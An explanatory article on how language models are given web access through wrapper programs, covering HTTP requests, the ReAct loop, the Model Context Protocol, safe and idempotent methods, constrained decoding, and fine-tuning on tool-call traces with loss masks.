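# How a language model is trained to make web requests and act on the responses, and how hard that is

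## What must be added to a text-only model before it can make a web request?

A language model is a computer program that takes in text and produces text. Its developers train it on a very large body of writing, after which it can answer questions, translate or write software. It cannot open a connection to another computer, so on its own it cannot look up today's weather, submit a form or delete a record. For that it needs a second, ordinary program that sends the web requests the model writes and adds the responses to the model's input. Engineers call this tool use, and usually call the combination of model and software an agent. *LLM Agents Are the Antidote to Walled Gardens* (Marro and Torr, 2025) defines an agent as a system that handles language, code or structured data and also works with outside tools or web pages.

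The added software can be short. In March 2023 the programmer Simon Willison published a working version in a few dozen lines of Python, in *A simple Python implementation of the ReAct pattern for LLMs*. It let OpenAI's GPT-3.5 search Wikipedia, search Willison's own blog and do arithmetic, though he warned that the code was not very robust. Most of the difficulty is in getting a model to write the right request at the right moment, and to keep doing so for many steps.

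### Predicting the next token

A token is a unit of text, often a word or part of one. The context is all the text the model can see at a given moment. From the context the model computes a probability for every token in its vocabulary:

P(next token | all the tokens before it)

A short routine picks one token according to the model's probabilities for the next token, adds it to the end of the context and runs the model again. Repeating this a few hundred times gives a paragraph. After "The capital of France is", the token for "Paris" gets a high probability. After "GET /index.html", the likely continuation is "HTTP/1.1", because many pages about programming contain that line. A base model has been trained only to predict the next token, and not yet to follow instructions or use tools.

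A model can write a valid web request, but the request is only text, so nothing happens. *MCP 2026 changes the rules* (Granados, 2026) describes how people use such a model. The model lists the steps, and the user carries them out, opening the calendar, finding the document and sending the email. The model also receives the results only if the user pastes them in, so it fills in missing information with guesses.

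### What a web request looks like

Programs on the web exchange messages under a set of rules called HTTP, the Hypertext Transfer Protocol. The current rules stand in the IETF's *rfc9110*, a 2022 standard from the Internet Engineering Task Force, the body that publishes the internet's technical standards. A client is a program that opens a connection in order to send requests. A server is a program that accepts connections and answers the requests with responses. Here is a request to an invented weather service:

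```
GET /cities?name=Springfield HTTP/1.1
Host: weather.example
Accept: application/json
```

And here is the response:

```
HTTP/1.1 200 OK
Content-Type: application/json

[{"id": 318, "city": "Springfield", "state": "Missouri"},
 {"id": 742, "city": "Springfield", "state": "Illinois"}]
```

The request opens with a method, GET, which is used to retrieve information. The address is split between the path, which follows the method, and the host, which is on the next line. Lines such as "Accept" are headers, which carry details about the message, in this case the format requested for the response. The response opens with a status code. A code of 200 means success, and 404 means the server found nothing at that address. The body follows the response's headers and a blank line, and here it is in JSON, a common notation for labelled data. Requests can have bodies too, mostly with the method POST,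 which is commonly used to submit data or cause a change. A service meant for use by other programs publishes its API, a documented list of the requests it accepts and the parameters each one takes.

*Mythra*, an undated proposal, is based on the fact that HTTP is text and language models generate text. Its demonstration used GPT-4 without fine-tuning (further training on chosen examples). The prompt described the addresses and parameters of a sample weather site, GPT-4 turned the user's question into an HTTP request, and the user's browser sent it.

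A text-only model cannot do the browser's part of a web request. The client has to look up the host's numerical address, open a connection to it and, for an encrypted site, check the server's certificate before sending the request. Newer versions of HTTP also encode messages differently without changing what they mean. Programmers have had libraries for this work for decades, and Willison's code does it all with one function call.

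Servers need no changes either, because a program that sends requests for a model is just another automated client. The IETF already counts light bulbs, household appliances and firmware scripts among the clients that start requests, and notes that a person doesn't have to be present when they do.

### The loop

The added software is the wrapper program, which some engineers call a harness or scaffold. It reads the model's output and looks for a tool call: a piece of text in an agreed format that the wrapper recognises as a request to act. In outline it does this:

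```
context = instructions + tool descriptions + user's task
steps = 0

repeat:
    output = run model on context, stopping at the end of a tool call
    context = context + output

    if output contains no tool call:
        return output                      # the final answer
    if steps == step_limit:
        return "stopped: step limit reached"

    call = parse the tool call
    if call is on the allowed list:
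        response = send the HTTP request, wait for the response
    else:
        response = "error: this call is not allowed"

    context = context + response
    steps = steps + 1
```

The model needs to stop generating at the end of a tool call. It predicts likely text, and the likely text after a request is a response, so if it continues, it will make up a plausible response and every later step will build on it. Willison handled this by instructing the model to write "PAUSE" after each action and end its message there, which mostly worked. But in one of his published examples, the wrapper supplied a real search result and the model then added its own line labelled "Observation", the label reserved for results. The line stated that Willison had visited a museum in Madagascar, when the retrieved text showed only that he had added the museum to a website. A wrapper that cuts off generation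 itself prevents a made-up response directly after a request, but it would not have prevented this one, because the model was by then writing its answer.

The pseudocode also shows that the model does not run while the request is in progress. The wrapper later starts it afresh on a longer context, and the text in that context is the model's only record of the task.

Without a step limit, a model that keeps writing tool calls would keep the loop running, and someone pays for each pass. Willison set his limit at five. His wrapper also had a list of three known actions and crashed if the model named any other. The pseudocode instead appends an error message, so the model can read it and try another call.

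### Two requests, the second depending on the first

Suppose a user asks, "Do I need an umbrella in Springfield, Illinois?" The wrapper offers two tools, one that finds a city's identifier from its name and one that fetches the weather for an identifier. The service does not accept city names in weather requests.

| Pass | The model | The wrapper program | The server |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads the question and the tool descriptions, and writes `find_city(name="Springfield")` | Stops generation, checks the call against its list, and sends `GET /cities?name=Springfield` | Searches its records and returns status 200 with two cities, numbers 318 and 742 |
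| 2 | Reads both entries, and writes `get_weather(city_id=742)` | Stops generation, checks the call, and sends `GET /weather?city=742` | Returns status 200 with `{"temp_c": 11, "sky": "rain"}` |
| 3 | Reads the weather data, and writes "Yes, it is raining there and 11 °C." | Finds no tool call and shows the text to the user | Receives nothing |

Between passes, the wrapper appends the server's response to the context. This is the only way the number 742 gets from the first response into the second request. HTTP is stateless, which the IETF defines to mean that a server can interpret each request on its own, so the weather server doesn't have to link the two requests.

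The model's part is therefore narrow, but easy to get wrong. It has to recognize that the request needs an identifier instead of a name, ask for that identifier, pick the right Springfield out of two, and copy the number exactly. If it copies 318, the wrapper sends a valid request, the server returns status 200, and the user gets a confident answer about Missouri. The status code shows only whether the request succeeded, so neither the wrapper nor the server can use it to check whether the request served the task.

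### Four forms a tool call can take

The example used named functions. Other formats use the same loop but differ in how much of the web the model can reach and in what the wrapper can check before acting.

| Form | Example of what the model writes | What it can reach | What the wrapper can check beforehand |
|---|---|---|---|
| Raw HTTP request | `GET /weather?city=742` with a host and headers | Any server the wrapper's network allows | Method, host and path, but not always what the server will do |
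| Named function | `get_weather(city_id=742)` | Only what the listed functions do | Function name, and the type and range of each argument |
| Browser command | `click("Continue")` | Any site a person can use, with or without an API | The command itself, whose effect depends on the page |
| Code | A Python script that sends requests | Anything the machine running it can reach | Very little without running it |

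With raw HTTP, the wrapper's developer has no work to do for each new service, because the model can use any API whose documentation it has seen. *Mythra* proposes that websites publish a plain text file describing their requests for this purpose. The wrapper can block requests to unknown hosts, or block every POST request. Beyond that, it can check only the path and parameters, which may not be enough to determine what the request will do on someone else's server.

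Named functions instead give the model less control over the request. A programmer writes each function, decides which server it contacts and fixes everything in the request except a few arguments. In Willison's Wikipedia tool, for example, the model supplies a search term and the code builds the rest of the address around it. But a function restricts the model only as much as its code does. Willison's "calculate" tool, which he described to the model as a way to run a calculation, passes the model's text to a Python command that will execute any Python expression. Even a strict check of the function name by the wrapper would not reveal this.

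A model can use browser commands on the many websites that have no public API. The wrapper drives a real browser, gives the model a description or picture of the page, and carries out clicks and keystrokes. In a position paper, Marro and Torr claim that a sufficiently advanced agent can replicate any computer interaction open to a human, so a company gains little by withholding an API. This is a forecast, and it depends mostly on what "sufficiently advanced" means. They also concede that browser control is less efficient than calling an API directly, that a small change to a page can break the agent's routine, and that site owners are taking countermeasures, such as Cloudflare, which carries traffic for many websites, leading suspected AI crawlers through decoy pages of nonsense. Browser commands are also hard to supervise, because a click on "Continue" might turn a page or place an order,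 and the wrapper can't distinguish the two without interpreting the page.

Code lets the model do the most in a single pass of the loop, but it is also the hardest form to check. One script can look up fifty cities, sort them by rainfall and send a message about each. Marro and Torr cite RestGPT, a system that reads descriptions of an API and generates Python to call it and convert the response into the format the user needs. No general method can predict everything a program will do, so operators who let models write code tend to rely on running the script on an isolated machine and limiting which servers it can contact.

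### The Model Context Protocol

A practical drawback of named functions is that somebody must write them. Connecting each of ten applications to fifty services takes five hundred separate connectors. A shared format reduces this to sixty implementations, one for each application and each service. Granados reports that Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, introduced such a format in 2024, called the Model Context Protocol (MCP).

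A service that supports MCP runs a small server. The wrapper sends it a "tools/list" message and gets back a list of the available functions and the arguments each one takes, which it puts into the model's context. When the model writes a tool call, the wrapper turns it into a "tools/call" message and sends it to the MCP server, which carries out the call. MCP Directory's *MCP 2026-07-28*, an independent explainer written when the latest version of MCP was still a release candidate, shows an example of the whole message as an ordinary HTTP POST with a few headers and a JSON body. The body gives the function, "search_issues", and its argument, the word "crash", which are the only parts the model writes.

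Developers have widely adopted the protocol. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026) reports more than 400 million downloads a month for the MCP software kits, four times the level at the start of the year. Automated systems download packages repeatedly, so the figure is better evidence of growth than of the number of users. The fifth version of the protocol, dated 28 July 2026, made its core stateless, like HTTP. It also added what the Model Context Protocol project calls header-based routing. In MCP Directory's example, the function's name appears in a header as well as in the body, so a company's network equipment could block one function and allow another without reading the JSON.

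In November 2026 the Model Context Protocol project moved to two releases a year and scheduled the next for 30 March 2027. It is also drafting an extension for files, in which the wrapper sends a file directly to its destination and the model handles only details such as the file's name and size. The draft requires the user's approval before the wrapper sends the file, or a policy set in advance if no user is present.

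### Reading and changing: GET, POST, "safe" and "idempotent"

The search for "crash" in the MCP example changes nothing on the server, but it is sent as a POST request. A wrapper that used only the HTTP method to distinguish reads from writes would misclassify it as a write. HTTP's designers did intend the method to indicate this difference, and the IETF's definitions are worth quoting exactly.

GET asks the server to transfer the current representation of whatever the address identifies. POST asks the server to process the enclosed body according to its own rules, and the IETF's examples include submitting a form, posting a message to a bulletin board and creating a new record. The weather service might accept this one:

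```
POST /alerts HTTP/1.1
Host: weather.example
Content-Type: application/json

{"city_id": 742, "when": "rain", "phone": "555-0142"}
```

The server creates a text-message alert and returns status 201, "Created". Creating the alert changes what the server stores, and programmers call such a change a side effect.

A method is safe if it is defined as "essentially read-only", meaning that the client neither requests nor expects any change on the server. GET is safe, but POST is not. A method is idempotent if sending the same request several times is meant to have the same effect as sending it once. Deletion is idempotent but not safe. Deleting record 742 changes the server, but deleting it again has no further effect.

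| Method | What the client asks for | Safe | Idempotent |
|---|---|---|---|
| GET | Fetch what is at this address | Yes | Yes |
| QUERY | Run the query in the body and return the result | Yes | Yes |
| POST | Process the body by the server's own rules | Not guaranteed | Not guaranteed |
| PUT | Replace what is at this address with the body | No | Yes |
| DELETE | Remove what is at this address | No | Yes |

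Many services use POST for plain searches, usually when the search is too long to fit in an address, and an outside program then cannot tell that the request is harmless. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (Reschke, Snell and Bishop, 2026) defined QUERY for these searches in June 2026. If services adopt it, a wrapper will be able to recognise more read-only requests by their method, but existing APIs will go on using POST for searches for some time.

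Idempotence matters when a connection fails. Suppose the server creates the rain alert but the connection drops before its response arrives. The wrapper then has no record of whether the request took effect. It could safely resend a GET, because duplicates of an idempotent request do no harm, as MDN's *Idempotent*, an entry in a widely used web reference, explains. But a second POST may create a second alert. The IETF therefore tells clients not to repeat such requests automatically unless repetition is known to be harmless or they can detect that the first attempt never took effect. Even if the wrapper follows this rule and appends "connection lost" to the context instead of resending, the model will most naturally write the same tool call again, and the wrapper will handle it as a new request.

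Safety, meanwhile, is a convention. The IETF defines it by what the client asks for, so a server may still do more. Servers routinely log each GET, and following an advertisement's link may charge the advertiser. More seriously, the IETF warns of sites that put commands in the address, such as "page?do=delete". It requires site owners to disable such commands for GET requests, since automated programs fetch every link they find, but HTTP has no way to enforce this. MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)* explains that server software such as Apache or Nginx can't enforce it either, because only the application behind it determines what a request does, and some applications do change data on a GET.

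The IETF distinguishes safe methods from unsafe ones so that automated programs can fetch pages without doing damage, and so that a client can restrict the unsafe methods when it handles untrusted content. Both reasons apply to a wrapper program with a language model attached. An obvious policy is to send every GET immediately and ask the user before any POST, and the standard permits the user to give that consent in advance through a setting. Under this policy, the user will sometimes have to approve a harmless search because it uses POST. The wrapper will also send a GET without asking, even if a badly built site treats it as an instruction to delete something.

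## Can a prompt alone produce the loop, without any training?

In 2021, researchers at OpenAI thought a prompt alone could not produce the loop. In *WebGPT*, Nakano, Hilton and colleagues (2021) connected GPT-3 to a text-only web browser that accepted ten commands, such as "Search", "Find in page" and "Back". They wrote that a base model, pre-trained only on ordinary text, could not use this browser because "it does not know the format of valid commands". So they collected about 6,000 demonstrations of people using the browser and trained the model on them.

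This was their reason for collecting demonstrations, not an experimental result. The claim is also quite narrow. Nakano and colleagues credit pre-training with the reading comprehension and answer-writing that the task needs, so the model mainly lacks the command format, which a developer can put in a prompt.

In June 2021, sharifshameem (2021) posted a thread about giving GPT-3 control of the Chrome browser and the objective "please buy me Airpods". The developer did no fine-tuning and used few-shot prompting, which means putting a few worked examples in the prompt before the real task. Each prompt also held the objective, the possible actions and a simplified copy of the web page. Most pages were too long for one prompt, so the program split them into pieces, got one proposed action for each piece, and then prompted GPT-3 again to choose among the proposals. GPT-3 reached the product page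 but then got sidetracked by Walmart's privacy policy.

In September 2022 the AI researcher Sergey Karayev connected GPT-3 to a Python interpreter, again using only a prompt. The prompt led GPT-3 to answer questions by writing short programs, including some that requested current stock prices from an API, according to The Decoder's *AI researchers push GPT-3's boundaries with Python*. The interpreter ran each program and showed the output to the user. This is a weaker example of the loop because the article doesn't describe GPT-3 reading a response and choosing a second request. Karayev advised against running the system on a personal computer because the model could also write code that wipes the hard drive.

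Neither demonstration includes a success rate, but the Chrome one shows that GPT-3 could issue usable browser commands without being trained on them.

### ReAct

Yao, Zhao and colleagues (2022), in *ReAct*, measured how well this works. Their main model was Google's PaLM-540B, a base model with 540 billion parameters (the adjustable numbers inside a model). The name ReAct joins "reasoning" and "acting", and the prompt format has three labelled parts:

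- A thought is free text in which the model plans or takes stock.
- An action is a tool call.
- An observation is the response, which the wrapper program adds.

In ReAct's notation, the context at step t is everything so far, c_t = (o_1, a_1, ..., a_{t-1}, o_t), where each o is an observation and each a is an action. An ordinary agent picks its next action from a fixed set A. ReAct enlarges the set to A ∪ L, where L is all possible language. Writing a thought â_t from L changes nothing outside the model and returns no observation. The thought is only added to the context, giving c_{t+1} = (c_t, â_t), so it can affect the task only through the text the model reads at the next step.

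For questions of fact, Yao and colleagues gave the model three actions on Wikipedia:

- `search[entity]` returns the first five sentences of the page with that name, or five similar names if no such page exists.
- `lookup[string]` returns the next sentence on the page that contains the string, like the "find" function in a browser.
- `finish[answer]` ends the task.

ReAct uses six full handwritten traces as examples for HotpotQA, a set of questions that each require two or more Wikipedia passages, and three for FEVER, a set of claims to check. More examples did not help. One of the HotpotQA examples asks for the elevation of the area into which the eastern sector of the Colorado orogeny (an episode of mountain building) extends. The trace begins with a search for the orogeny, followed by a lookup of "eastern sector", which shows that it reaches the High Plains. A search for "High Plains"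 returns a notice that the name has two meanings, so the next search is for "High Plains (United States)", and the trace ends with the answer "1,800 to 7,000 ft". The example shows the model the format, how to carry a name from one response into the next request, and what to do when a response is ambiguous.

These are the results with PaLM-540B:

| Method | What the model does | HotpotQA, % exact match | FEVER, % correct |
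|---|---|---|---|
| Standard | Answers directly | 28.7 | 57.1 |
| Chain of thought | Reasons in writing, then answers | 29.4 | 56.3 |
| Majority vote | Takes the commonest answer from 21 chains of thought | 33.4 | 60.4 |
| Act | Uses Wikipedia but writes no thoughts | 25.7 | 58.9 |
| ReAct | Uses Wikipedia and writes thoughts | 27.4 | 60.9 |
| ReAct, then vote | Votes if ReAct runs out of steps | 35.1 | 62.0 |
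| Vote, then ReAct | Uses ReAct if under half the votes agree | 34.2 | 64.6 |
| Best trained systems of the time | Varies | 67.5 | 89.5 |

The loop worked, but on HotpotQA the model did slightly worse with Wikipedia than without it, partly because Yao and colleagues deliberately made the search tool weak so that the model would have to reason about what to look for. In a sample of ReAct's wrong answers, they attributed 23% to searches that returned nothing useful and 47% to reasoning errors, including runs where the model got stuck repeating itself. None came from invented facts, which accounted for 56% of the failures with chain of thought alone.

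ReAct did better on tasks that consist mainly of acting. ALFWorld is a text game of household chores in which the model may have to search dozens of places for an object. With two worked examples in the prompt, ReAct succeeded in 71% of games with the best of six prompts and 57% on average. The best prompt without thoughts succeeded in 45%. BUTLER, a system trained on 100,000 expert traces for each type of chore, succeeded in 37%, but it was a weak baseline, since a GPT-2 model fine-tuned on 3,553 games had already done much better. On WebShop, a simulated shop with 1.18 million real products, ReAct succeeded 40.0% of the time with one worked example, compared with 29.1% for a model trained on 1,012 human traces and 59.6% for expert humans.

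### When training matters

Yao and colleagues also tried PaLM models with 8 billion and 62 billion parameters on HotpotQA. With prompting alone, ReAct performed worst of the four basic methods at both sizes. They attribute this to the difficulty of learning both reasoning and acting from a handful of examples.

The ReAct paper also fine-tuned the smaller models on 3,000 traces that prompted ReAct had generated and that ended in a correct answer. On these models, ReAct was the worst method with prompting and the best after fine-tuning. The fine-tuned 8-billion-parameter model beat every prompting method on the 62-billion model, and the fine-tuned 62-billion model beat every prompting method on the 540-billion one. On this benchmark, fine-tuning on 3,000 examples helped more than making the model about eight times larger.

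Practice with HotpotQA questions could account for some of the improvement, but models that Yao and colleagues fine-tuned to answer the questions without Wikipedia did significantly worse than the ones that learned to use it. Their explanation is that training without Wikipedia teaches a model to memorise facts, while training with it teaches the model how to find them.

The experiment also trained the small models on working traces that the large model produced from a prompt, with only a few traces written by hand.

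### Why a prompt can be enough

The usual explanation is that pre-training text contains source code that sends web requests, API documentation with sample calls and responses, and logs of exchanges between programs and servers. A model that can predict the next line of such a document has much of what it needs to write a tool call. The prompt supplies details such as the names of the tools and the labels for each part of a trace. When the prompt contains several traces in the same format followed by a new question, the most likely continuation is another trace in that format.

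Prompted models have been observed writing working calls. It is plausible that they can do so because their training data contains code and API documentation, but this is an inference. The direct test would be to train two otherwise identical models, one without such documents, and give both the same prompt.

The closest evidence comes from models of similar size but different training data. *APTBench* (Qin, Xi and colleagues, 2025) tested base models on software and research tasks. Qwen3-4B averaged 38.75 on the software tasks, against 24.34 for SmolLM3-3B. Qin and colleagues attribute such gaps to whether developers chose the pre-training data with agents in mind, but the models differ in other ways too, so the evidence is suggestive at best. *AliceAI-Foundation-80B-A3B-Base* (2026) describes a more direct comparison. A model without tool-use data in pre-training fell well behind a Qwen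 base model on most agent benchmarks, and adding such data closed much of the gap. However, both models had some further training before the test, and the added data was tool-use traces, not ordinary code.

There is also evidence about what the examples in the prompt contribute. Verma, Bhambri and Kambhampati (2024), in *On the Brittle Foundations of ReAct Prompting for Agentic Large Language Models*, reran ReAct on ALFWorld with newer models and changed one part of the prompt at a time. Moving all the thoughts to the start of the example, so that they no longer alternated with actions, improved results for the three GPT models and lowered them a little for Claude Opus. But replacing both worked examples with examples of a different chore was disastrous:

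| Model | Success with examples of the same chore, % | Success with examples of a different chore, % |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 Turbo | 27.6 | 1.6 |
| GPT-3.5 Instruct | 44.7 | 5.2 |
| GPT-4 | 23.3 | 0 |
| Claude Opus | 56.6 | 6.6 |

The available actions were the same for every chore, so knowing the format was not enough. GPT-3.5 Instruct fell from 52% to 9% when the examples showed how to place one object and the task was to place two. Verma and colleagues conclude that the models mostly imitate the most similar example and do not reason about the task. That fits their results, but they tested models from 2023 and 2024 in one text game, so the conclusion may not hold for current models.

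By then, developers could often leave out the worked traces and just describe the format, because their models were already fine-tuned to follow instructions. In *From Language Models to Practical Self-Improving Computer Agents*, Sheng (2024) gave a GPT-4 model access to a computer's command line and a long page of rules. One rule forbids the model to write "examples" of commands, because the wrapper will execute anything in a command block. In one case study, the model wrote its own internet search tool and then used it. A person gave instructions throughout, and Sheng says the cases may be cherry-picked.

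### Base models in 2025 and 2026

In 2025 Qin and colleagues still considered it infeasible to run a base model on a full agent task, so they tested single steps instead. They gave the model the task so far, usually with three worked examples, and checked whether the next command it wrote matched the expected one exactly. When the task was installing research software, Qwen3-1.7B got 19.9% right, Qwen3-4B got 31.6%, and Kimi K2, with a trillion parameters, got 40.7%. Exact matching can undercount correct answers, since two different commands can do the same job.

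A year later Oh, Zeng and colleagues (2026), in *Sharpening Tax in Post-Training*, ran base models on full tasks anyway. They used a simple prompt and a wrapper that was lenient about how the model wrote its tool calls. They report pass@1, the share of single attempts that succeed, and pass@32, the chance that at least one of 32 attempts does. If c out of n attempts at a task succeed, then

pass@k = 1 − C(n − c, k) / C(n, k)

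where C(n, k) is the number of ways to choose k attempts from n. The averages for eight base models were:

| Benchmark | pass@1 without the added prompt and lenient wrapper, % | pass@1 with them, % | pass@32 without, % | pass@32 with, % |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| BFCL (multi-step tool calls) | 5.6 | 15.6 | 15.2 | 49.1 |
| WebShop | 6.3 | 9.7 | 39.5 | 49.2 |
| ACEBench (tool use) | 44.2 | 42.6 | 89.3 | 87.7 |

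A current base model can run the whole loop from a prompt, but unreliably. The high pass@32 figures are less useful than they look, because a model that succeeds in one attempt out of twenty has an 81% chance of at least one success in 32 independent attempts. Repeated attempts are fine in a simulator, where researchers can reset everything and a program checks which attempt worked, but on a live shopping site the failed attempts might have placed orders.

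Some developers now include tool-use traces in pre-training, as with the AliceAI model, so a 2026 base model may have seen thousands of tool calls before anyone prompts it. PaLM probably had not, since few such traces existed when Google trained it. The 2022 results are therefore better evidence that a prompt can produce the loop in a model trained only on ordinary text, even though the 2026 models are much more capable.

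### Malformed calls and small models

Larger models now have little trouble with format. *Enhancing Tool Calling in LLMs with the International Tool Calling Dataset* (2026) reports that DeepSeek-V3 and Qwen2.5-Coder-32B matched the required format more than 99% of the time without training on the task. But DeepSeek-V3 scored only 75.5 out of 100 at filling in parameters, and that was the best result among the open models. Two smaller models already trained to use tools did badly on format because they wrote calls in the style they had learned and left out the reasoning that the new format required.

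Prompting alone is less reliable with very small models. In *Beyond Fluent Generation*, Shahriar and Mastoi (2026) tested five models with under 2 billion parameters on 100 prompts. The task was about as easy as tool use gets, since every prompt named the tool and listed all the values to put in the call. Qwen2.5-1.5B got up to 79% right, while Phi-1.5 got none and the other two models from outside the Qwen family never exceeded 7%. In 588 of the 658 failures, the researchers' program could not extract valid JSON from the output. The model filled in a wrong value in only three.

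Even the good scores depended on that program to strip away surrounding text. Only 5 of the 1,000 outputs were valid JSON without it. The program kept everything from the first opening brace to the last closing one, and the models could write up to 150 tokens, so a perfect call followed by a second one would have failed. Some of these failures may therefore come from not stopping in time.

*Small agents should know what their tools do* (2026) found a similar pattern in Phi-4-mini, which mostly explained what it would do and wrote the call as a block of Python. Fine-tuning raised its score on one part of BFCL, but about a third of the gain came from formatting alone, since a more lenient parser could already recover that much from the untuned model's output. The format failures may also have prevented some destructive calls. On simulated commerce tasks, three untuned models made 1, 2 and 2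 destructive calls without asking for confirmation, and their fine-tuned versions made 45, 6 and 39.

### Stop sequences

A stop sequence is text that makes the software running the model end generation as soon as it appears. In the ReAct format, the obvious choice is the label "Observation:". The model writes its action and then the label, following the pattern of the examples in the prompt, and the software stops it before it can invent a response. Base models need this most, because nothing else makes them stop at the end of a call. After the final answer, a base model may well write another question, since that is what came next in the examples.

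A stop sequence on the label would also have cut off the extra "Observation" in Willison's Madagascar example. But the model could have made the same false statement in its answer, and no stop sequence prevents that.

Yao and colleagues found that models prompted with ReAct sometimes kept repeating the same thought and action. They suspected the cause was greedy decoding, which always picks the most probable token, and suggested trying other ways of choosing tokens. A repeated call is still well formed, so checking its format won't catch the repetition. The wrapper has to compare it with earlier calls.

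### Grammar-constrained decoding

Constrained decoding prevents malformed calls while the model is writing them. The developer supplies a grammar, a formal description of every valid output. Before each token, the software works out which tokens the grammar allows, sets the probability of all others to zero and scales up the rest:

P′(t) = P(t) / (sum of P over all allowed tokens), if t is allowed, and 0 otherwise

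The weather service from earlier needs a city's number. Suppose the model has written `get_weather(city_id=` and gives "Springfield" a probability of 0.6, "742" 0.3 and "318" 0.1, treating each as one token. If the grammar allows only numbers, "Springfield" is ruled out, and the probabilities of "742" and "318" rise to 0.75 and 0.25. The call will now be valid, but there is still a one in four chance that the model chooses 318, the number for Springfield, Missouri.

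Tests on small models show the same division. *Constrained Decoding Eliminates Structural Failures in Small LLMs* (2026) reports that a constrained model with 1 billion parameters beat an unconstrained one with 3 billion on 14 hand-designed tasks, but constraints didn't help when the model had misunderstood the instruction. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* (2026) tested models on writing programs rather than tool calls, and found that a well-matched constraint helped a model with 2 billion parameters more than one with 32 billion. *Accelerating Constrained Decoding with Token Space Compression* (2026) found that constrained models usually still fell short of 100% valid output. This can happen when a model reaches its length limit before finishing its output.

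Reports of how much constrained decoding slows responses vary widely. *When Correct Isn't Usable* (2026) measured responses that took 3.6 to 8.2 times as long on school maths problems, while *Constrained Decoding Eliminates Structural Failures in Small LLMs* describes the overhead of a tool called XGrammar as near zero. The slowdown depends heavily on the grammar. A newer version of XGrammar failed to finish a batch of tests in 24 hours when given the full grammar of an unfamiliar programming language, which is far more complex than a list of tool names and arguments.

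A grammar can also cause mistakes. If it requires one of ten tool names, the model has to call a tool even when none is relevant. *Repair, Not Improvement* (2026) gives the example of a system that calls a weather API in response to a legal question. The developer can fix this by adding "no tool" to the permitted outputs.

A call that the model makes too early is harder to fix. *Towards Reliable Benchmarking* (2025) found that, for every model, over 66% of failures on multi-step tasks involved a value that no earlier call had yet returned. Suppose the model requests the weather before it has looked up the city's number. Without a grammar, it might write "Springfield", and the wrapper would reject the call and append an error message. A grammar that allows only numbers would force it to write a number anyway, and the wrapper would send the request.

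## How is a model fine-tuned on request-response traces?

A grammar can force a model to write a city number, but it can't make the model more likely to write 742 than 318. Fine-tuning can. The developer collects traces of completed tasks, and the training software adjusts the model's parameters to make the requests in those traces more probable. The traces already contain the server's responses as text, so training doesn't send any web requests.

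### From a trace to a training example

A trace starts as a list of messages, each labelled with a role that shows whether it contains the developer's instructions, the user's question, the model's output or a tool's response. The model reads a single sequence of tokens, so a small script called the chat template joins the messages and puts markers between them. Many of these markers are special tokens, vocabulary entries reserved for structure. In Llama 3.1, for example, two special tokens enclose the name of the role at the start of each message.

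Tool calls have a format of their own. Luv Verma (2026), in *What Broke & Why*, a practitioner's book about training language models on one or a few processors, describes the format in Qwen3.5, a family of open models from Alibaba. With the markers put into words, a weather request in that format looks like this:

```
[tool call begins]
[function: get_weather]
[parameter: city_id]  742  [parameter ends]
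[function ends]
[tool call ends]
```

Other models put a JSON object between the two outer markers. The call then takes its place in the full training example:

| Part of the sequence | What it contains | Where the text comes from | Must the model learn to write it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Tool description | The name of each function and its arguments | The developer | No |
| Question | The user's task | The user | No |
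| Request | Any reasoning, then the tool call | The model | Yes |
| End-of-turn token | A signal that the model has finished | The model | Yes |
| Response | The data that the server returned | The server, through the wrapper program | No |
| Answer | The reply to the user | The model | Yes |
| End-of-turn token | The same signal again | The model | Yes |

The fine-tuned model learns to write an end-of-turn token as soon as the request is complete, and the software stops generation there, just as it would at a stop sequence with a base model. If the developer forgets to train the model to write this token, the model may continue and make up a response.

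Special tokens can also appear in the wrong place. *Dissecting model behavior through agent trajectories* (2026) describes a run in which gpt-oss-120b, an open model from OpenAI, tried to read part of a source file. A control token appeared in the tool's name, and the wrapper rejected the name as invalid. The model could not see the stray token and treated the rejection as its own misuse of the tool. It retried without success, then ran a search instead of reading the file.

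The wrapper has to use the same format that the model learned. Luv Verma warns that if the formats differ, the model writes calls that the wrapper can't parse, and an evaluation that uses the training format won't reveal the problem.

### The loss mask

Fine-tuning uses the same objective as pre-training, but usually counts only some of the tokens. If x_t is the token at position t, the training software minimises

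L = −Σ m_t log p(x_t | earlier tokens)

The loss mask m_t is 1 for tokens the model must write and 0 for tokens it only reads. Suppose the next token the model must write is "742", and the model gives it a probability of 0.3. This token adds −ln 0.3, or 1.20, to the loss. If training raises the probability to 0.9, the token adds 0.11.

A short trace might have 40 tokens of question, 30 of request, 600 of response and 50 of answer. The mask is 1 for the request and the answer, so the model trains on 80 of the 720 tokens, or 11%. Without a mask, the server's response would make up 83% of the training targets, and the request, the part the developer most wants the model to learn, would make up 4%.

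The model still reads the other 640 tokens. To raise the probability of "742" in a second request, training has to change how the model uses the first response, because the number appears there. *ReToolSQL* (2026), which trains a model to query databases, therefore keeps the returned rows in the context and excludes them only from the loss.

Building the mask is simple in principle, but mistakes are easy to make and hard to notice. *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) gives code that finds the marker at the start of the model's message and computes the loss on what follows. This works for one question and one answer. In a trace with several requests, the code must also find where each of the model's messages ends, or it will include the responses that come next in the loss.

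Luv Verma reports a worse case with Qwen3.5. Hugging Face's TRL, a popular training library, has an option to train only on the model's own messages, which it finds through labels in the chat template. Qwen3.5's template doesn't contain those labels, so the option either produces an error or sets the whole mask to zero, depending on the library version. In the second case, the run continues but the model learns nothing useful. The fix is a two-line change to the template, plus a check that the mask contains at least one 1. Verma also recommends building the mask while assembling the trace, when the source of each piece of text is still known, and then checking one example by eye.

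The choice of which parts of a call to train on can also affect how well a model constructs calls. In *Agentic On-Policy Distillation Implicitly Reshapes LLMs' ReAct Patterns* (2026), a model learned from a stronger model's feedback on its own attempts. It constructed calls differently well when the training software masked the feedback on the markers around tool calls, or on the whole call. The software located each call by counting opening and closing markers, so an unmatched opening marker could mistakenly extend the mask over the model's later messages.

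### Does training on responses teach a model to invent them?

The usual argument for the mask is that a model trained on every token learns to predict both requests and responses. In the 720-token example, it would get twenty times as much practice at writing weather data as at requesting it. Luv Verma says that this teaches a model to "hallucinate the environment", meaning that it writes what a tool would probably have returned instead of calling the tool. The loss still falls smoothly, so the developer gets no warning. *AgentMath* (2025), which trains a model to solve maths problems with a code interpreter, also masks the interpreter's outputs, to keep the model from memorising them.

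The argument is plausible, but the end-of-turn token and the wrapper should already prevent the model from writing a fake response directly after a call. The greater risk is probably that the model will skip the call and make up a result in its reasoning or answer.

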